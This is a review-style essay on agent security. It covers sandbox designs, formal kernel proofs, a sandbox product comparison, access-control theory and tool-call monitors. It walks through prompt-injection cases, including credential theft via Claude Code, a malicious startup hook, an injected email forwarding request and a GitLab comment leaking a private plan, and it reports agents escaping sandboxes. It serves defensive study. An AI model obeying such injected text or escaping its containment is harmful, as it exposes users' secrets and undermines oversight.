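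Safeguards in the model do much worse when the user unknowingly passes on the attack. In February 2026 an Anthropic researcher, testing the company's own defences, tricked a colleague into giving Claude Code a prompt that looked like routine instructions. One step told Claude to send the colleague's cloud credentials to an outside server, and Claude did so in 24 of 25 runs. The request came from the user, so a classifier had nothing unusual to detect. Blocking connections to unknown servers would have stopped the theft no matter who wrote the prompt, as would keeping the credentials outside the sandbox.

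Anthropic does not rely on isolation alone, and it advises developers to contain the agent first and then add safeguards in the model. Its products are still a good test of whether stronger isolation is enough, because they use three kinds of isolation and the company has described where each fell short.

### Three designs at Anthropic

On the chat service claude.ai, Claude runs code in a gVisor container on Anthropic's servers. The container's files last for one session, and the code has no access to the user's computer. The isolation is meant to protect Anthropic's infrastructure and its other customers. Its trusted base includes gVisor, the host's system-call filter, and the surrounding network configuration, internal authentication and orchestration. Anthropic concentrated its review on the last three, which are newer, because attackers had been testing gVisor and the filter for years.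 Anthropic does not report moving anything out of this sandbox later. The drawback is that Claude has no lasting workspace and cannot work directly on the user's files.

Claude Code needs those files, so it runs on the developer's machine. At first it could read freely but had to ask before writing, running a command or using the network. Anthropic then added the shell sandbox, which uses Seatbelt on macOS and bubblewrap on Linux. The trusted base includes the host's kernel and the part of Claude Code that decides whether each command runs in the sandbox. An injected instruction or a tired user can cause that part to let a command run outside it. Sandboxed commands can also still read most of the files the user can read. In the February test, the default sandbox would probably have let Claude read the credentials and then blocked the upload.

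The harness was outside this boundary from the start, which helps explain the flaws in Claude Code's trust prompt. In the simplest of three cases reported to Anthropic between mid-2025 and January 2026, a repository's settings file defined a hook that Claude Code ran at startup. A sandbox around the agent's shell commands could not have stopped this, because the harness itself launched the attacker's code. Anthropic fixed the flaw by making Claude Code wait to read project settings until the user accepts the project.

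Claude Cowork, a desktop agent for general office work, has the strongest isolation of the three because many of its users cannot judge whether a shell command is safe. It runs code in a virtual machine with its own Linux kernel, on top of the hypervisor that Apple or Microsoft supplies. Code in the machine can reach only two folders on the host, one that the user selects and one that holds Claude's settings. The user's credentials stay in the host's keychain, and the virtual machine gets a limited token for each session. Users can also share a folder as read-only, or as writable but without permission to delete. A small mistake could still undo the boundary. If the software checks whether a path is allowed before it resolves symbolic links, which are files that point to other locations, a link inside the shared folder could lead outside it.

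In the first version of Cowork, the agent loop ran inside the virtual machine too, so no process on the host had the authority to make an exception. Anthropic has since moved the loop to the host because Cowork was unusable when the machine failed to start. Now Claude can still reply and help find the fault. Anthropic also moved local tool servers to the host, because they were hard to audit inside the machine and some had to work with other programs on the host, such as databases.

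The virtual machine used to enclose the whole agent, but the loop now runs outside it and only the code that Claude executes runs inside. Anthropic considers the security impact of this change minimal because that code is still confined. That seems right for the code, but the loop handles text that an attacker may have written, and it is now part of the trusted base. A local tool server has the same access as any other program the user installs.

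Anthropic found that the hypervisor, gVisor and the system-call filter were dependable across its products, but that a proxy it had written itself to enforce a list of approved network destinations failed. It advises developers to prefer components that have survived years of attack. This is sensible, although a company's list of known incidents cannot rule out escapes that nobody noticed. The proxy is also a weaker example than Anthropic suggests, because it checked the destination correctly and the data left through an approved one. A better-tested proxy with the same rule would have let the data through too.

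### What the seL4 proofs state

The case for mature components rests on their track record, and for seL4 it also rests on a mathematical proof. seL4 is a microkernel, a small operating-system kernel that does only the work that needs the processor's privileged mode and leaves file systems and device drivers to ordinary programs. Heiser (2026), in *seL4*, puts its size at 10,000 to 12,000 lines of code, compared with tens of millions for a mainstream operating system. Programs can refer to the kernel's objects only through capabilities.

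In 2013, Murray, Matichuk and colleagues completed a proof, presented in *seL4*, that the seL4 kernel controls the flow of information. Their threat model suits agents well. They assume that all code outside the kernel is malicious once the system has started, that the malicious programs work together, and that the attacker knows the kernel's code and configuration. The security goal is that a program can learn about another part of the system only where the policy permits it.

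The proof builds on two earlier ones. The first, of functional correctness, shows that the C code does only what an abstract specification allows. For a starting state *s* and a sequence of events *e*, let C(*s*, *e*) be the set of states the code can reach and A(*s*, *e*) the set the specification allows. The theorem is that C(*s*, *e*) ⊆ A(*s*, *e*) for every *s* and *e*. Murray and colleagues could therefore reason about the much simpler specification and carry the result over to the 8,830 lines of C.

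The second is integrity. The policy is a graph in which each node is a subject and each arrow is a kind of authority, such as "read". By the integrity theorem, any change to the system's state must be one that the policy lets the running subject make. If subject S2 may read S1's memory but has no other authority over S1, then nothing in S1 changes while S2 runs, even during a system call. By a companion theorem, no step gives a subject more authority than the policy records. Together, the two theorems extend the guarantee to runs of any length, by the same kind of induction that Bell and LaPadula used.

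Integrity limits what a program can change, but the program might still learn a secret. For the information-flow proof, Murray and colleagues divide the system into partitions, each with its own memory and kernel objects. Let sources(*n*, *s*, *p*) be the set of partitions that may send information to partition *p*, directly or through others, during the next *n* steps from state *s*. Their theorem, called nonleakage, is that if two reachable states *s* and *t* agree on the scheduler's private data and on every partition in that set, then *p* will have the same contents after the system runs for *n* steps from either state.

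In the coding agent example, the agent is in partition *p* and the cloud key is in a partition that may not send anything to *p*. States *s* and *t* can differ in the value of the key, but the agent's partition ends up the same either way, so the agent cannot have learned anything about the key.

The proof only needs to cover one step at a time. If the running partition may not send information to *p*, the integrity theorem already shows that it cannot change *p*. Otherwise, the proof must show that the kernel passes on only what the policy allows. Some of the hardest cases involved one-way messages, where Murray and colleagues had to prove that the sender learns nothing about the receiver by sending a message.

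### What the seL4 proofs assume

The information-flow theorem applies only to systems configured in a particular way. The policy must match the initial distribution of capabilities. The kernel's timer must be the only source of interrupts, so device drivers have to keep checking their devices for new data. Channels between partitions must also be permanent, a condition added because the proof exposed a leak. seL4 deletes an object when the last capability to it disappears, so a partition that deleted its capability could learn whether another partition also held one. Murray and colleagues prevent this by requiring a spare copy of each such capability where no partition can reach it.

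According to the seL4 Foundation's *What the Proofs Assume*, the proofs also assume that about 340 lines of Arm assembly code and about 1,200 lines of boot code are correct, and that the hardware behaves as the formal model predicts. Devices that access memory directly must be absent or well behaved, because they could otherwise overwrite the kernel. The confidentiality proof does not cover timing channels, such as the one Lampson described in which a program signals by varying how much it computes. Heiser says the proofs currently apply only when the kernel runs on a single processor core.

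These limits match where people have found bugs. The seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Proofs* reports no functional-correctness defects in verified code since that proof was finished in 2009. It does report defects in unverified configurations, including those that support multiple cores or Intel's virtualization extensions, both of which a typical agent server would use. The Foundation's *seL4 News* for 2026 describes a release that fixed problems in code the proofs do not cover, and thanks Anthropic for reporting some of them.

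Proving seL4's functional correctness took about 25 person-years by Murray and colleagues' count, and the information flow proof took another 51 person-months. Agents also need Linux and its tools, which are far too large to verify in this way but can run inside a partition. The example in *seL4 Enforces Integrity* uses a large, untrusted copy of Linux as a network router and relies on the kernel to keep it within its limits. According to a talk at the seL4 Summit (2026), the security proofs for 64-bit Arm processors now cover the virtual processors that such guest systems use.

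Cloud customers can already rent something similar. InfoQ (2026) reports that Amazon's Graviton5 servers, which use the Nitro Isolation Engine, are the first in a major public cloud to run formally verified isolation between virtual machines in production. According to the announcement *Nitro Isolation Engine*, the integrity proof shows that operations on one virtual machine leave the private state of every other machine unchanged. The confidentiality proof is similar to seL4's and makes an exception for permitted flows of information out of a machine. These proofs concern the protection of one customer's machine from another's, and they show that isolation can be formally verified in systems used outside research.

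### Five sandbox products compared

Most agents run on engines without such a proof, so buyers need other evidence. *AI Code Sandboxes* (Andronchik and Lokhmakov, 2026) compares five products that run AI-written code, each installed with its default settings on the same type of Linux host. The threat model is an operator who runs untrusted code on infrastructure they trust. It excludes attacks between customers, attacks on the software that manages the sandboxes, and leaks through the processor's hardware.

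They examined six properties:

- How much of the host's kernel the sandbox exposes
- What the code inside can learn about the host
- Whether the operator can add further Linux protections
- How many vulnerabilities researchers have published
- How quickly fixes reach users
- How thoroughly the developers fuzz the engine, which means feeding it large amounts of generated input to find bugs

For the first property, they picked 14 kernel features that past exploits had used and counted how many were reachable. For the second, they ran 28 checks for details such as the host's disk serial numbers.

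| Product (engine) | Type | Risky features reachable, of 14 | Host details leaked, of 28 | Published flaws in two years (those that could allow escape) | Engine version, May 2026 | Public continuous fuzzing |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Arrakis (Cloud Hypervisor) | MicroVM | 12 | 1 | 2 (1) | Unchanged for 471 days | No |
| E2B, self-hosted (Firecracker) | MicroVM | 7 | 0 | 2 (2) | Unchanged for 399 days | No |
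| Microsandbox (libkrun) | MicroVM | 11 | 0 | 0 | Updated every 1–3 months | No |
| gVisor (runsc) | Second kernel | 5 | 2 | 3 (0) | Current | Yes |
| Daytona (runc) | Container | 11 | 10 | 4 (4) | Current | Limited |

The type of engine predicts some of these results. Daytona's container shares the host's kernel, which explains most of its ten leaks and exposes it to the kernel's flaws. About 3,500 flaws in the Linux kernel were published over the same two years, compared with 11 in all five engines together. But products with the same type of engine differ a lot. Arrakis and E2B both use microVMs, yet Arrakis exposes 12 of the risky features and E2B exposes 7.

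A sandbox with a small attack surface can still have vulnerabilities. Firecracker allows its own process only 55 system calls, the fewest that Andronchik and Lokhmakov measured, but both of its recent flaws could help an attacker cross the boundary. One was in its emulation of a device and the other in the program that sets up its confinement. This system call filter limits which parts of the host's kernel an attacker can reach through Firecracker, but it cannot remove bugs in Firecracker itself.

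For the operator, the product's update policy mattered more than how fast the engine's developers fixed bugs. Cloud Hypervisor usually published a flaw and its fix on the same day, but Arrakis kept using a version from February 2025 through 12 later releases, two of which fixed serious flaws. E2B's self-hosted default had gone at least 44 days without the fix for one of the Firecracker flaws. Daytona had the weakest isolation of the five but was up to date. It also ran its containers in a privileged mode, which prevented operators from adding several standard Linux protections.

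libkrun's lack of known flaws may mean only that few people have looked for them. Andronchik and Lokhmakov found no public fuzzing or academic study of libkrun, and they leave it out of their ranking on this measure. Fuzzing also helps only if somebody runs it. Cloud Hypervisor's one recent flaw that could allow escape was in a component with its own fuzzing program, but the project's automated checks only compiled that program and never ran it. An outside reviewer found the flaw by hand.

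Andronchik and Lokhmakov decline to combine their measurements into an overall score, and none of the five products fully met their thresholds on all four questions. gVisor did best on resistance to escape. The measurements describe software as of May 2026, and a single update could change several of them. Being able to reach a risky feature also doesn't mean being able to exploit it. More importantly, the study covers only the engines and leaves network rules and the handling of secrets for a second part. It can help a buyer choose stronger isolation, but it doesn't show whether an agent holding a cloud key can send that key to a stranger.

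### When the agent attacks the sandbox

A sandbox may be less effective against an AI agent than against ordinary untrusted code. A typical malicious program carries an attack prepared in advance, while a capable agent can look for a new one from inside the sandbox. The agent doesn't have to be malicious to do this. Anthropic has seen Claude models escape a sandbox just to complete a task. *Using a VM to Contain an AI Agent* (Schneier, 2026) quotes an experimenter who concluded that an off-the-shelf virtual machine is not enough to contain a modern AI agent with strong hacking skills.

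People who favour isolation can reply that the experimenter used the wrong kind of virtual machine. A reader's comment under Schneier's post quotes the experimenter's account of trying the agent against Firecracker, where it crashed the machine but did not escape. The experimenter recommends engines with little attack surface, along with minimal privileges, logging, active monitoring and a limit on how long the agent can run. A small engine is probably harder to escape, but the experimenter thought the agent might have managed it with more time. Slow updates also become more dangerous, because an agent that can find unknown flaws can presumably use published ones too.

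A verified kernel is a more complete answer, at least for the code that the proof covers, but it is harder to adopt. Heiser writes that seL4 comes without a file system, networking or device drivers, and that designing a good system on top of it takes rare expertise, although newer frameworks are making this easier. A company that runs its agents in the cloud can rent a verified hypervisor instead, but that does not help a developer whose agent runs on a laptop.

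### What security software cannot see

Isolation also hides the agent from defenders. Many companies install endpoint detection software, which monitors the programs on each computer for signs of an attack. When they evaluated Cowork, their security teams asked why this software could not monitor activity inside the virtual machine. The isolation that protects the rest of the computer from Claude's code also blocks the security software, so everything inside the virtual machine appears on the host as one opaque process.

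In response, Anthropic lets administrators export event logs, though it admits these are no substitute for live monitoring. Logs may also fail to reveal the most important attack, in which injected text leads an agent to send data through a service it is allowed to use, because they show only a successful, authorized request. Anthropic therefore prefers to inspect what tools return before the model reads it, using proxies in Claude Code and Cowork. This restores some visibility, but it relies on a classifier that can make mistakes, and strong isolation was supposed to reduce the need for such safeguards.

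### What the boundary lets through

A boundary does not control how the agent uses whatever somebody deliberately let in, and better engineering cannot change that. Cowork's virtual machine protects the rest of the computer, but a hijacked agent can still damage a folder that the user gave it write access to. The seL4 theorem has the same limit. If the policy puts the cloud key in the agent's partition and lets that partition send data to the network, the theorem still holds when the agent sends the key to an attacker, because the policy permits that flow.

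Developers can already limit what an agent can reach by sharing one folder instead of a home directory, making it read-only, and keeping the original credentials outside the sandbox. These measures work and don't require a formal model, but they help less when the task requires the access. For example, a proxy outside the sandbox might hold the developer's publishing token and add it to the agent's requests. The agent couldn't steal the token, but an attacker could still make it a confused deputy by using a malicious bug report to persuade it to publish a harmful version of the software. The proxy would supply the token for that request too.

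Removing the access would prevent this, but it would also stop the agent from publishing the bug fix. Anthropic now advises treating each approved network destination as a grant of every function the agent can reach there. Under that rule, a developer who approves a code host has to consider what the agent could publish, delete or share on it, however strong the virtual machine is.

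## The view that established access control can be extended to agents

Access control can check each function an agent tries to use on a code host, so approving the host need not give the agent every function it can reach there. For example, a monitor between the agent and the host could let the agent open a pull request in one repository and refuse everything else. On this view, agents fail mostly because their developers ignore old principles. Under least privilege, a program gets only the rights its task needs. Under complete mediation, a monitor checks every access, as Anderson required. In a capability system, a program can use a resource only if somebody has given it a token for that resource.

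These principles address failures like one in Australia described by the Coalition for Secure AI (CoSAI, 2026). A Claude-powered agent that was booking a gym class discovered that the booking service did not check who owned a reservation, and it cancelled a stranger's without being asked. The agent had legitimate access to the cancellation function, and the service limited which functions it could call but not whose bookings it could change. An ordinary ownership check would have stopped the cancellation, but a stronger virtual machine would not have, because the agent had not escaped from anything.

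Companies make similar mistakes in their own agents. *Lessons from Penetration Tests on Large-Scale Agent Systems* (Eykholt, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) describes two tests that IBM researchers ran in 2025 on proprietary products. One product, an assistant that fixes bugs reported on GitHub, checked each terminal command against a list of approved strings, but some approved programs could start other programs, so the testers could run whatever they liked. The assistant's container also had access to copies of other repositories that used the assistant. The development team had treated a user's request for help with a bug report as consent to anything the agent did next. Preventing these flaws would not have required a new theory of security, though two tests cannot show how common such flaws are.

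Christodorescu and colleagues examined 11 attacks on real agents and matched each to the principles it violated, including least privilege and complete mediation. Most of the attacks also involved an insecure flow of information, which is harder to fix with better permissions.

### Five assumptions that agents weaken

Access control usually relies on assumptions about the program it governs, and an Android app meets them fairly well. Its code exists before installation, its developer chooses permissions from a list, and each permission refers to something a person can understand, such as the camera.

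| Assumption | What agents do to it | Consequence |
|---|---|---|
| The program is fixed | The model chooses its steps as it reads | Nobody can analyse the code beforehand to see which rights it needs |
| A developer writes the policy | The user may type only a sentence | Somebody has to infer the policy from the request |
| A subject's identity stands for its intent | Injected text can redirect an agent that keeps its user's identity | A request can pass the identity check and still serve an attacker |
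| Objects and rights are stable | Agents find resources, create files and start other agents | Rights can be missing or out of date by the next step |
| The interface has meaningful operations | Some agents click, type or run shell commands | A rule about the operation may not control its effect |

Without a fixed program, it is hard even to define the least privilege for a task. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) gives the example of an agent that has to write a report from approved records. The agent could process the records locally or send a larger dataset to an online analysis service. The second plan may need every permission it includes, even though the task can be done without them. The paper suggests looking for an adequate plan with *A*(π) ⊆ *G* before asking for more permissions, where *A*(π) is the set of permissions that plan π requires and *G* is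 the set the agent already has. The choice between plans is not always clear, since one may need access to sensitive local files and another may disclose less sensitive data to an outsider.

An app's developer can explain why the app needs the camera. An agent's task has no developer to explain what access it needs, and a user who asks an agent to "sort out my travel" has probably not thought about which accounts that involves.

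Identity is a weak guide to intent because the operating system identifies the same user whether the agent is following the user's request or an attacker's. *AgenticOS* (Zhao, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), by researchers at Tencent and a Chinese university, describes a mismatch between the task users authorize and the general operations operating systems grant, such as opening files and network connections. Each operation may be harmless by itself, but an attacker can combine them into something the user never asked for. The paper proposes an operating system that would give an agent only specific functions, such as uploading a named report, and no general network access. It presents a design and does not describe an implementation of the agent's runtime.

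Rights can also go out of date when a tool changes. Zhou and Zhang point out that a tool might start forwarding data to an outside service while keeping the same name and inputs. An existing permission to call the tool would then allow a disclosure that nobody had approved.

Earlier programs also broke these assumptions. Anderson's panel expected malicious users to write their own programs, and web browsers run code that arrives while a page is open. Christodorescu and colleagues compare an agent that finds new instructions to a browser that loads new scripts. A browser can usually identify the address a script came from and restrict the script accordingly, but an agent often cannot identify an instruction's source. The older methods can therefore help secure agents, but they need information about where instructions came from, which current agents tend to lose.

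### Commenting on GitLab issue 745

Christodorescu and colleagues illustrate the problem with a browser agent that gets two requests in a row. The user first types "comment on GitLab issue 745 that we're done" and then "summarize issue 745 for me". They write out the rights for the first request, and the same reasoning gives the rights for the second:

| Request | Open issue 745 | Write in its comment box | Anything else in GitLab or the browser session |
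|---|---|---|---|
| Comment that the work is done | Yes | Yes | No |
| Summarize the issue | Yes | No | No |

Each row is simple, but moving from one to the other is difficult. By the time the second request arrives, the agent has opened the issue, and its context may contain text from anyone who could post there. The system could erase the context and derive a new policy from the second request alone, which is secure but makes the agent forget what it learned during the first task. If the system instead keeps the context and has a model derive the new policy from it, an attacker's text can influence the policy.

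Adding the new rights to the old ones would be worse. The agent would read the whole issue while still able to comment, so an injected instruction could make it post something. The table also doesn't allow for a second issue that issue 745 depends on. A good summary may need that issue, but the only evidence for granting access might be a sentence in issue 745 itself.

Christodorescu and colleagues recommend policy languages that support formal reasoning, so that software can determine how a new rule changes the agent's overall rights. Computer scientists have known since 1976 that such reasoning has limits.

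### Whether a right can leak

Harrison, Ruzzo and Ullman (1976), in *Protection in Operating Systems*, asked whether a program can always determine if someone will be able to acquire a right they should not have. A state in their model is a triple (*S*, *O*, *P*), made up of the set of subjects, the set of objects and the access matrix. Commands change the matrix. Each command tests whether certain rights are present and, if they are, makes a fixed list of basic changes. A basic change enters or deletes a right, or creates or destroys a subject or object.

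For example, one command lets a file's owner share it. If *P*[owner, file] contains "own", the command enters "read" into *P*[friend, file]. In their example, a process called Sam creates a file called Data, which makes Sam its owner, and then runs this command, which changes Joe's cell for Data from empty to {read}. The safety question is whether any sequence of commands could put a given right into a cell that did not have it before, leaving aside people trusted to share that right.

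They proved that no algorithm can answer this question for every system. The proof makes an access matrix imitate a Turing machine, the standard mathematical model of a computer. Each square of the machine's tape becomes a subject, and rights in the matrix record the symbols on the tape and the position of the machine's head. The commands add one particular right only if the machine reaches its final state. An algorithm that could always detect leaks could therefore tell whether any given program will eventually stop, which Turing had proved impossible.

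The question is easier in restricted systems. Harrison and colleagues gave an algorithm for systems in which every command makes only one basic change, but admitted that these are "not terribly realistic". Even creating a file and becoming its owner takes two changes. If no command can create subjects or objects, a matrix with *k* kinds of right, |*S*| subjects and |*O*| objects has at most 2 to the power *k*|*S*||*O*| possible states, so a program can in principle check them all. In the take-grant model, which has four fixed rules for changing rights, an algorithm can settle the question in time proportional to the size of the system.

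Even in the general case, a search can find leaks. *Towards a Uniform Framework for Dynamic Analysis of Access Control Models* (2017) describes heuristic methods that look for a sequence of commands leading to one. A thorough search will eventually find a leak if one exists, but it may run forever if none does. *Safety Analysis in the NGAC Model* (2025) reports that several widely circulated proofs about how hard the problem is contained errors, which Tripunitara and Li later corrected.

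A reference monitor only has to decide whether to allow an agent's current request, so it doesn't have to predict what the agent will do. For example, it can refuse a request to read a key without knowing why the agent made it. *SoK* (2025), a survey of trust and authorization in agents, nevertheless concludes that static access control fails "catastrophically" for agents. It argues that an agent with memory and tools can carry out any computation, so predicting whether it will take a sensitive action is as hard as the halting problem.

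In their 1976 result, Harrison and colleagues already assumed that commands could arrive in any order, so the difficulty comes from the rules for changing rights, not from unpredictable agents. They also warned that the theorem does not rule out proving a particular system safe. They compared this to grammars, where no algorithm can tell whether an arbitrary grammar is ambiguous, but people can write one for a programming language and prove it unambiguous.

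If an agent can create other agents, add resources and rewrite its own permissions through general-purpose commands, there may be no way to determine which rights it could end up with. This is mainly a reason to keep the rules for acquiring rights simple. The problem is manageable if the agent can only lose rights, or gain them from a short approved list. Even a proof that no right can leak would not show that the agent will use its rights well.

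### Progent's rules for tool calls

Progent checks each tool call an agent makes against a list of rules. Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, give each rule an effect (allow or forbid), the name of a tool, conditions on the tool's inputs and a fallback for blocked calls. In their notation, a rule for sending Slack messages might look like this:

`allow send_slack_msg when { to == "alice" }, fallback return "Recipient not allowed"`

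When the agent calls a tool, Progent applies that tool's forbid rules before its allow rules. It blocks any call that matches no rule. By default, the agent gets an error message and can try another way to finish the task.

In Shi and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list in an email. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The list includes sending a summary of recent emails to the user's Slack account, so a language model proposes rules for reading email, looking up the account and sending Slack messages. When the lookup shows that the account name is "alice", the model narrows the Slack rule to that recipient. One of the recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to an attacker. No rule allows the agent to send email, so Progent blocks the call.

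The same model that proposed the useful rules could also propose a rule that helps an attacker. Progent therefore uses an SMT solver, a program that decides whether logical formulas can be true, to compare each proposed policy *P*′ with the current policy *P*. The solver checks whether *A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*), where *A*(*P*) is the set of tool calls that *P* allows. If so, the new policy allows nothing new and takes effect automatically. Otherwise, it needs approval. Shi and colleagues call this property monotonic confinement. It avoids the hard cases of the 1976 problem because the agent cannot gain any rights between approvals.

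This answers much of an earlier criticism. *Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* objected that Progent's updates depended on a language model to filter out malicious instructions. With the solver, a fooled model can no longer expand the policy by itself, unless the user has set Progent to approve every request. Somebody still has to tell good expansions from bad ones, though, and in the example both kinds originate in an email. Shi and colleagues report that only 6% of updates in one benchmark needed approval. This keeps the burden low, but the few remaining requests are the ones that most need careful judgment. (Progent greatly reduced successful attacks on two benchmarks even when the tests assumed that the user approved every expansion.)

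The sample rule also controls a message's recipient but not its content. Shi and colleagues exclude attacks that stay within the rights a task needs, such as a seller's text that persuades a shopping agent to prefer the seller's product over other valid options.

### Rights that end during the task

A right that is appropriate at one stage of a task can be unnecessary at the next. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents Portico, a monitor that revokes such rights from coding agents. A person or organization first supplies a task contract, which lists the resources available from the start, those the agent may request, the events that end each grant, and anything always forbidden.

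Suppose an agent's task is to add a timeout setting to a program. The agent starts with access to the main source file and its test. Under the contract, the agent may also request a second file, `serialization.py`, but never the packaging notes. When the agent requests the second file, Portico issues handles, which are opaque tokens tied to this task, file, kind of access and grant. The agent can then read and edit the file. Once the tests pass, Portico revokes the handles and removes them from the list of actions it shows the agent. If the agent tries an old handle, the monitor rejects it before anything happens.

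Only trusted events can end or renew a grant. A test counts as trusted if Portico launched it, but the model's statement that it has finished does not. In the GitLab example, posting the comment could end the agent's right to comment, so the agent would no longer have that right when it summarized the issue.

Santos-Grueiro compared Portico with a monitor that issued the same grants at the same times but never revoked them. Portico rejected all 10 attempts to reuse an expired right, while the other monitor permitted all 10. This confirms that revocation works, but the test's design nearly guaranteed the result, and the test did not measure how often agents would misuse leftover rights. In another small test, the monitor blocked 84 forbidden proposals when the agent was shown a broader set of possible actions, up from 67, which suggests that hiding unneeded options also helps.

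The guarantee depends on the contract and on a catalogue that correctly translates each tool call into the resources it affects. Shell commands are difficult to translate, and Portico either requests approval for a command it cannot classify or denies it. Revoking access also cannot remove information the agent has already read into its context.

*Sandlock* (Wang and Zheng, 2026) applies a similar idea to the processes an agent starts. Installing packages usually requires the network, while running the project's tests may not. Sandlock enforces fixed rules, such as which folders a process may write to, in the Linux kernel. A supervisor outside the sandbox handles decisions that depend on what happens during the run. When the sandboxed code tries to start a new program, the supervisor pauses it and notifies the software that runs the agent. That software can then cut off the network before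 the tests begin, without restarting the sandbox.

The supervisor must prevent a program from changing a request between the check and the action. When a process asks to connect to a server, the supervisor copies the address, checks the copy and uses it to make the connection itself, so the connection is unaffected if another part of the process changes the original address. Sandlock adds about 5 milliseconds to a command's start time, so an agent can use it for many short steps.

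Wang and Zheng warn that the name of a program is only a hint, because an attacker can rename a forbidden tool or write a new one. Cutting off the network works whatever the program is called, but it does not help if a malicious package sends data to an allowed server during installation, when the process still has legitimate network access. Their threat model also trusts the software that runs the agent, and that software would have to recognize when one stage ends and another begins.

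### Web requests instead of clicks

Rules about operations are especially hard to write for browser agents. A click at the same position on the screen might open an email on one page and delete it on another. Blocking one route to a website does not help much. In *ceLLMate*, Meng, Feng and colleagues (2025) stopped an agent from going directly to a website, but it found the site through a search engine and clicked the result.

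The ceLLMate system checks the requests that the browser sends to a site's server. A purchase eventually requires a request to place an order, however the agent clicks and types. The site's developers would write a file called an agent sitemap, which links each type of request to a named action such as "PlaceOrder". In the GitLab example, posting a comment and adding an access key for a new user would be different actions, even if the agent could do both with ordinary clicks.

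To enforce the rule "spend no more than $50 on Amazon", ceLLMate intercepts the request to place an order. The request does not contain the total, so a browser extension reads it from the checkout page beforehand. A proxy between the agent and the browser slows the agent so that the page can update. Otherwise, ceLLMate could check an old total after the agent has added another item. An agent could still place two orders for $49 each, so ceLLMate can count orders and allow only one.

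This restores meaningful operations, but it depends on websites to describe their functions. Meng and colleagues wrote a sitemap for 51 of GitLab's functions by hand, and they expect site owners to maintain such files to protect their users. If a sitemap omits an action or describes it incorrectly, the agent is no better protected for that action than it is today. They also state that ceLLMate does not track whether untrusted text caused a request. A product review could persuade the agent to buy the wrong $40 coffee maker, and the purchase would satisfy the rule.

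### Identity and delegation

Agents increasingly hand parts of their work to other agents. Zhou and Zhang survey methods that give each agent its own identity and a signed credential stating whom it represents and what it may do. Separate credentials are better than sharing the user's password because a service can tell the agents apart and revoke one agent's access without affecting the rest.

CoSAI recommends that authority stay the same or narrow each time one agent delegates to another. Some credentials enforce this mathematically. For example, an agent holding a type of token called a macaroon can add a restriction by combining it with the token's current signature to make a new signature. The next agent receives only the new signature and cannot recover the old one, so it cannot remove the restriction, but it can add more before passing the token on.

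Narrower credentials can still add up to too much authority. In one of Zhou and Zhang's examples, a user authorizes the purchase of one item, and the agent delegates the job to two others, each of which may buy one. Together they can buy two items without either exceeding its limit. To prevent this, the agents need a shared record of whether the authorized purchase is still available. An agent must check the record and reserve the purchase in a single step, or both could find it available and go ahead.

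A timeout creates a similar problem. If the shop does not respond, the purchase may still have gone through, and trying again could buy a second item. Programmers usually solve this by giving each operation an identifier, so that the shop can recognize a repeated request. But an agent may change the order or try a different shop after the timeout, and then the identifier no longer matches. Revoking the agent's credential would stop another attempt but would not cancel the original purchase.

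Restrictions can also be lost when one system translates them for another. A user might allow an agent to send one summary to Alice, while the mail service offers only a general permission to send email. The service could check the agent's credential correctly and still let the agent send anything to anyone. Zhou and Zhang require that the original policy allow every effect that the credentials and checks allow. A monitor in front of the mail service could enforce the missing limits. CoSAI advises refusing the delegation if a service cannot express those limits.

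Identity and delegation show who sent a request and on whose authority, but not whose text led the agent to send it.

### Which confused deputies remain

Capabilities solve the version of the confused deputy problem that Tymshare encountered, as Hardy argued. On a Unix system, a small launcher can do the same job as the token system by opening the debugging file with the user's permissions and passing the compiler the open file instead of its name.

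The same approach protects agents from many attacks. If a bug report tells a coding agent to post the cloud key, the agent cannot do so without a token for the key. If the gym had given the agent a token for its user's reservation instead of a general right to cancel reservations, the agent could not have cancelled anyone else's.

In 2016, Rajani, Garg and Rezk compared access control with capabilities in a small programming language, in *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*. In the access-control version, the system checks each time a program writes to a location. In the capability version, a program cannot obtain a token for a location it has no right to change. Both versions guarantee that no program writes where it lacks authority. They then gave what they believed to be the first formal definition of when a program is free from confused deputy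 attacks, and proved that capabilities do not always prevent these attacks.

The exceptions arise when an attacker influences the deputy's choice without handing it a token. Suppose a compiler properly holds tokens for the billing file and an output file, and uses a number from the user to decide which to write to. A user who enters the right number can make the compiler overwrite the billing file without naming it or holding a token for it. Rajani and colleagues found restrictions on programs that would rule out such cases, but the restrictions made the language useless for almost all practical purposes.

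An agent that reads a stranger's text is in much the same position, with the text in place of the number. For example, an agent may have permission to read a private release plan and to comment on issue 745, because the user wants it to reply to a customer. Someone then comments on the issue, asking the agent to include the unreleased features in its reply. If the agent complies, the plan becomes public, even though the agent rightly holds both capabilities and the monitor finds that both the read and the comment are permitted. Making the tokens harder to forge would not prevent this, nor would revoking them after the reply.

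According to Zhou and Zhang, an agent would need to distinguish evidence about how to carry out its instructions from requests for new permissions. If its instructions are to send a report to the company's contact, a trusted directory can supply evidence that the contact is Alice. An instruction in a document to copy Bob as well would require a new permission, which the document has no authority to grant. The model receives both as text in the same context and may act on either. A rule that lists Alice as the only recipient would stop the copy to Bob, but would not stop a document from changing what the agent sends to Alice.

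Developers can reduce the problem by splitting a task into a series of stages. Wang and Zheng's system can run these stages separately, so that no stage both reads untrusted text and has network access. They acknowledge that a single sandbox often cannot enforce this separation, because one legitimate step may need private data, outside text and the network at once. The stages also have to exchange some information to be useful, and an attacker may be able to influence what passes between them.

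Rajani and colleagues proposed tracking where each value came from, including the values that influenced a program's choices. They proved that a system that does this fully can prevent confused deputy attacks without the restrictions that capabilities place on programs. For the release plan, a monitor would need a record that the reply drew on private text and that a stranger's comment had prompted it, and the agent's list of rights contains neither fact.

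## The view that the flow of data must be controlled as well as access

A monitor that checks one request at a time approves both steps of the release plan attack, because the harm comes from the data that passes between them. One of the real attacks that Christodorescu and colleagues examined, a prompt injection against OpenAI's ChatGPT Operator browser agent, is an even clearer case. They found an insecure flow of information and a failed human check, but no breach of least privilege or complete mediation. Supporters of information-flow control conclude that a monitor must also track where data came from and where it is going.

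### Noninterference

The strictest form of this idea is noninterference, which Goguen and Meseguer defined in 1982. One group of users does not interfere with another if nothing the first group does changes what the second can see. For a program *P* that handles secret and public data, write *s* ≈ *t* when two starting states agree on everything public. *P* satisfies noninterference if, for all *s* and *t*:

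*s* ≈ *t* implies *P*(*s*) ≈ *P*(*t*)

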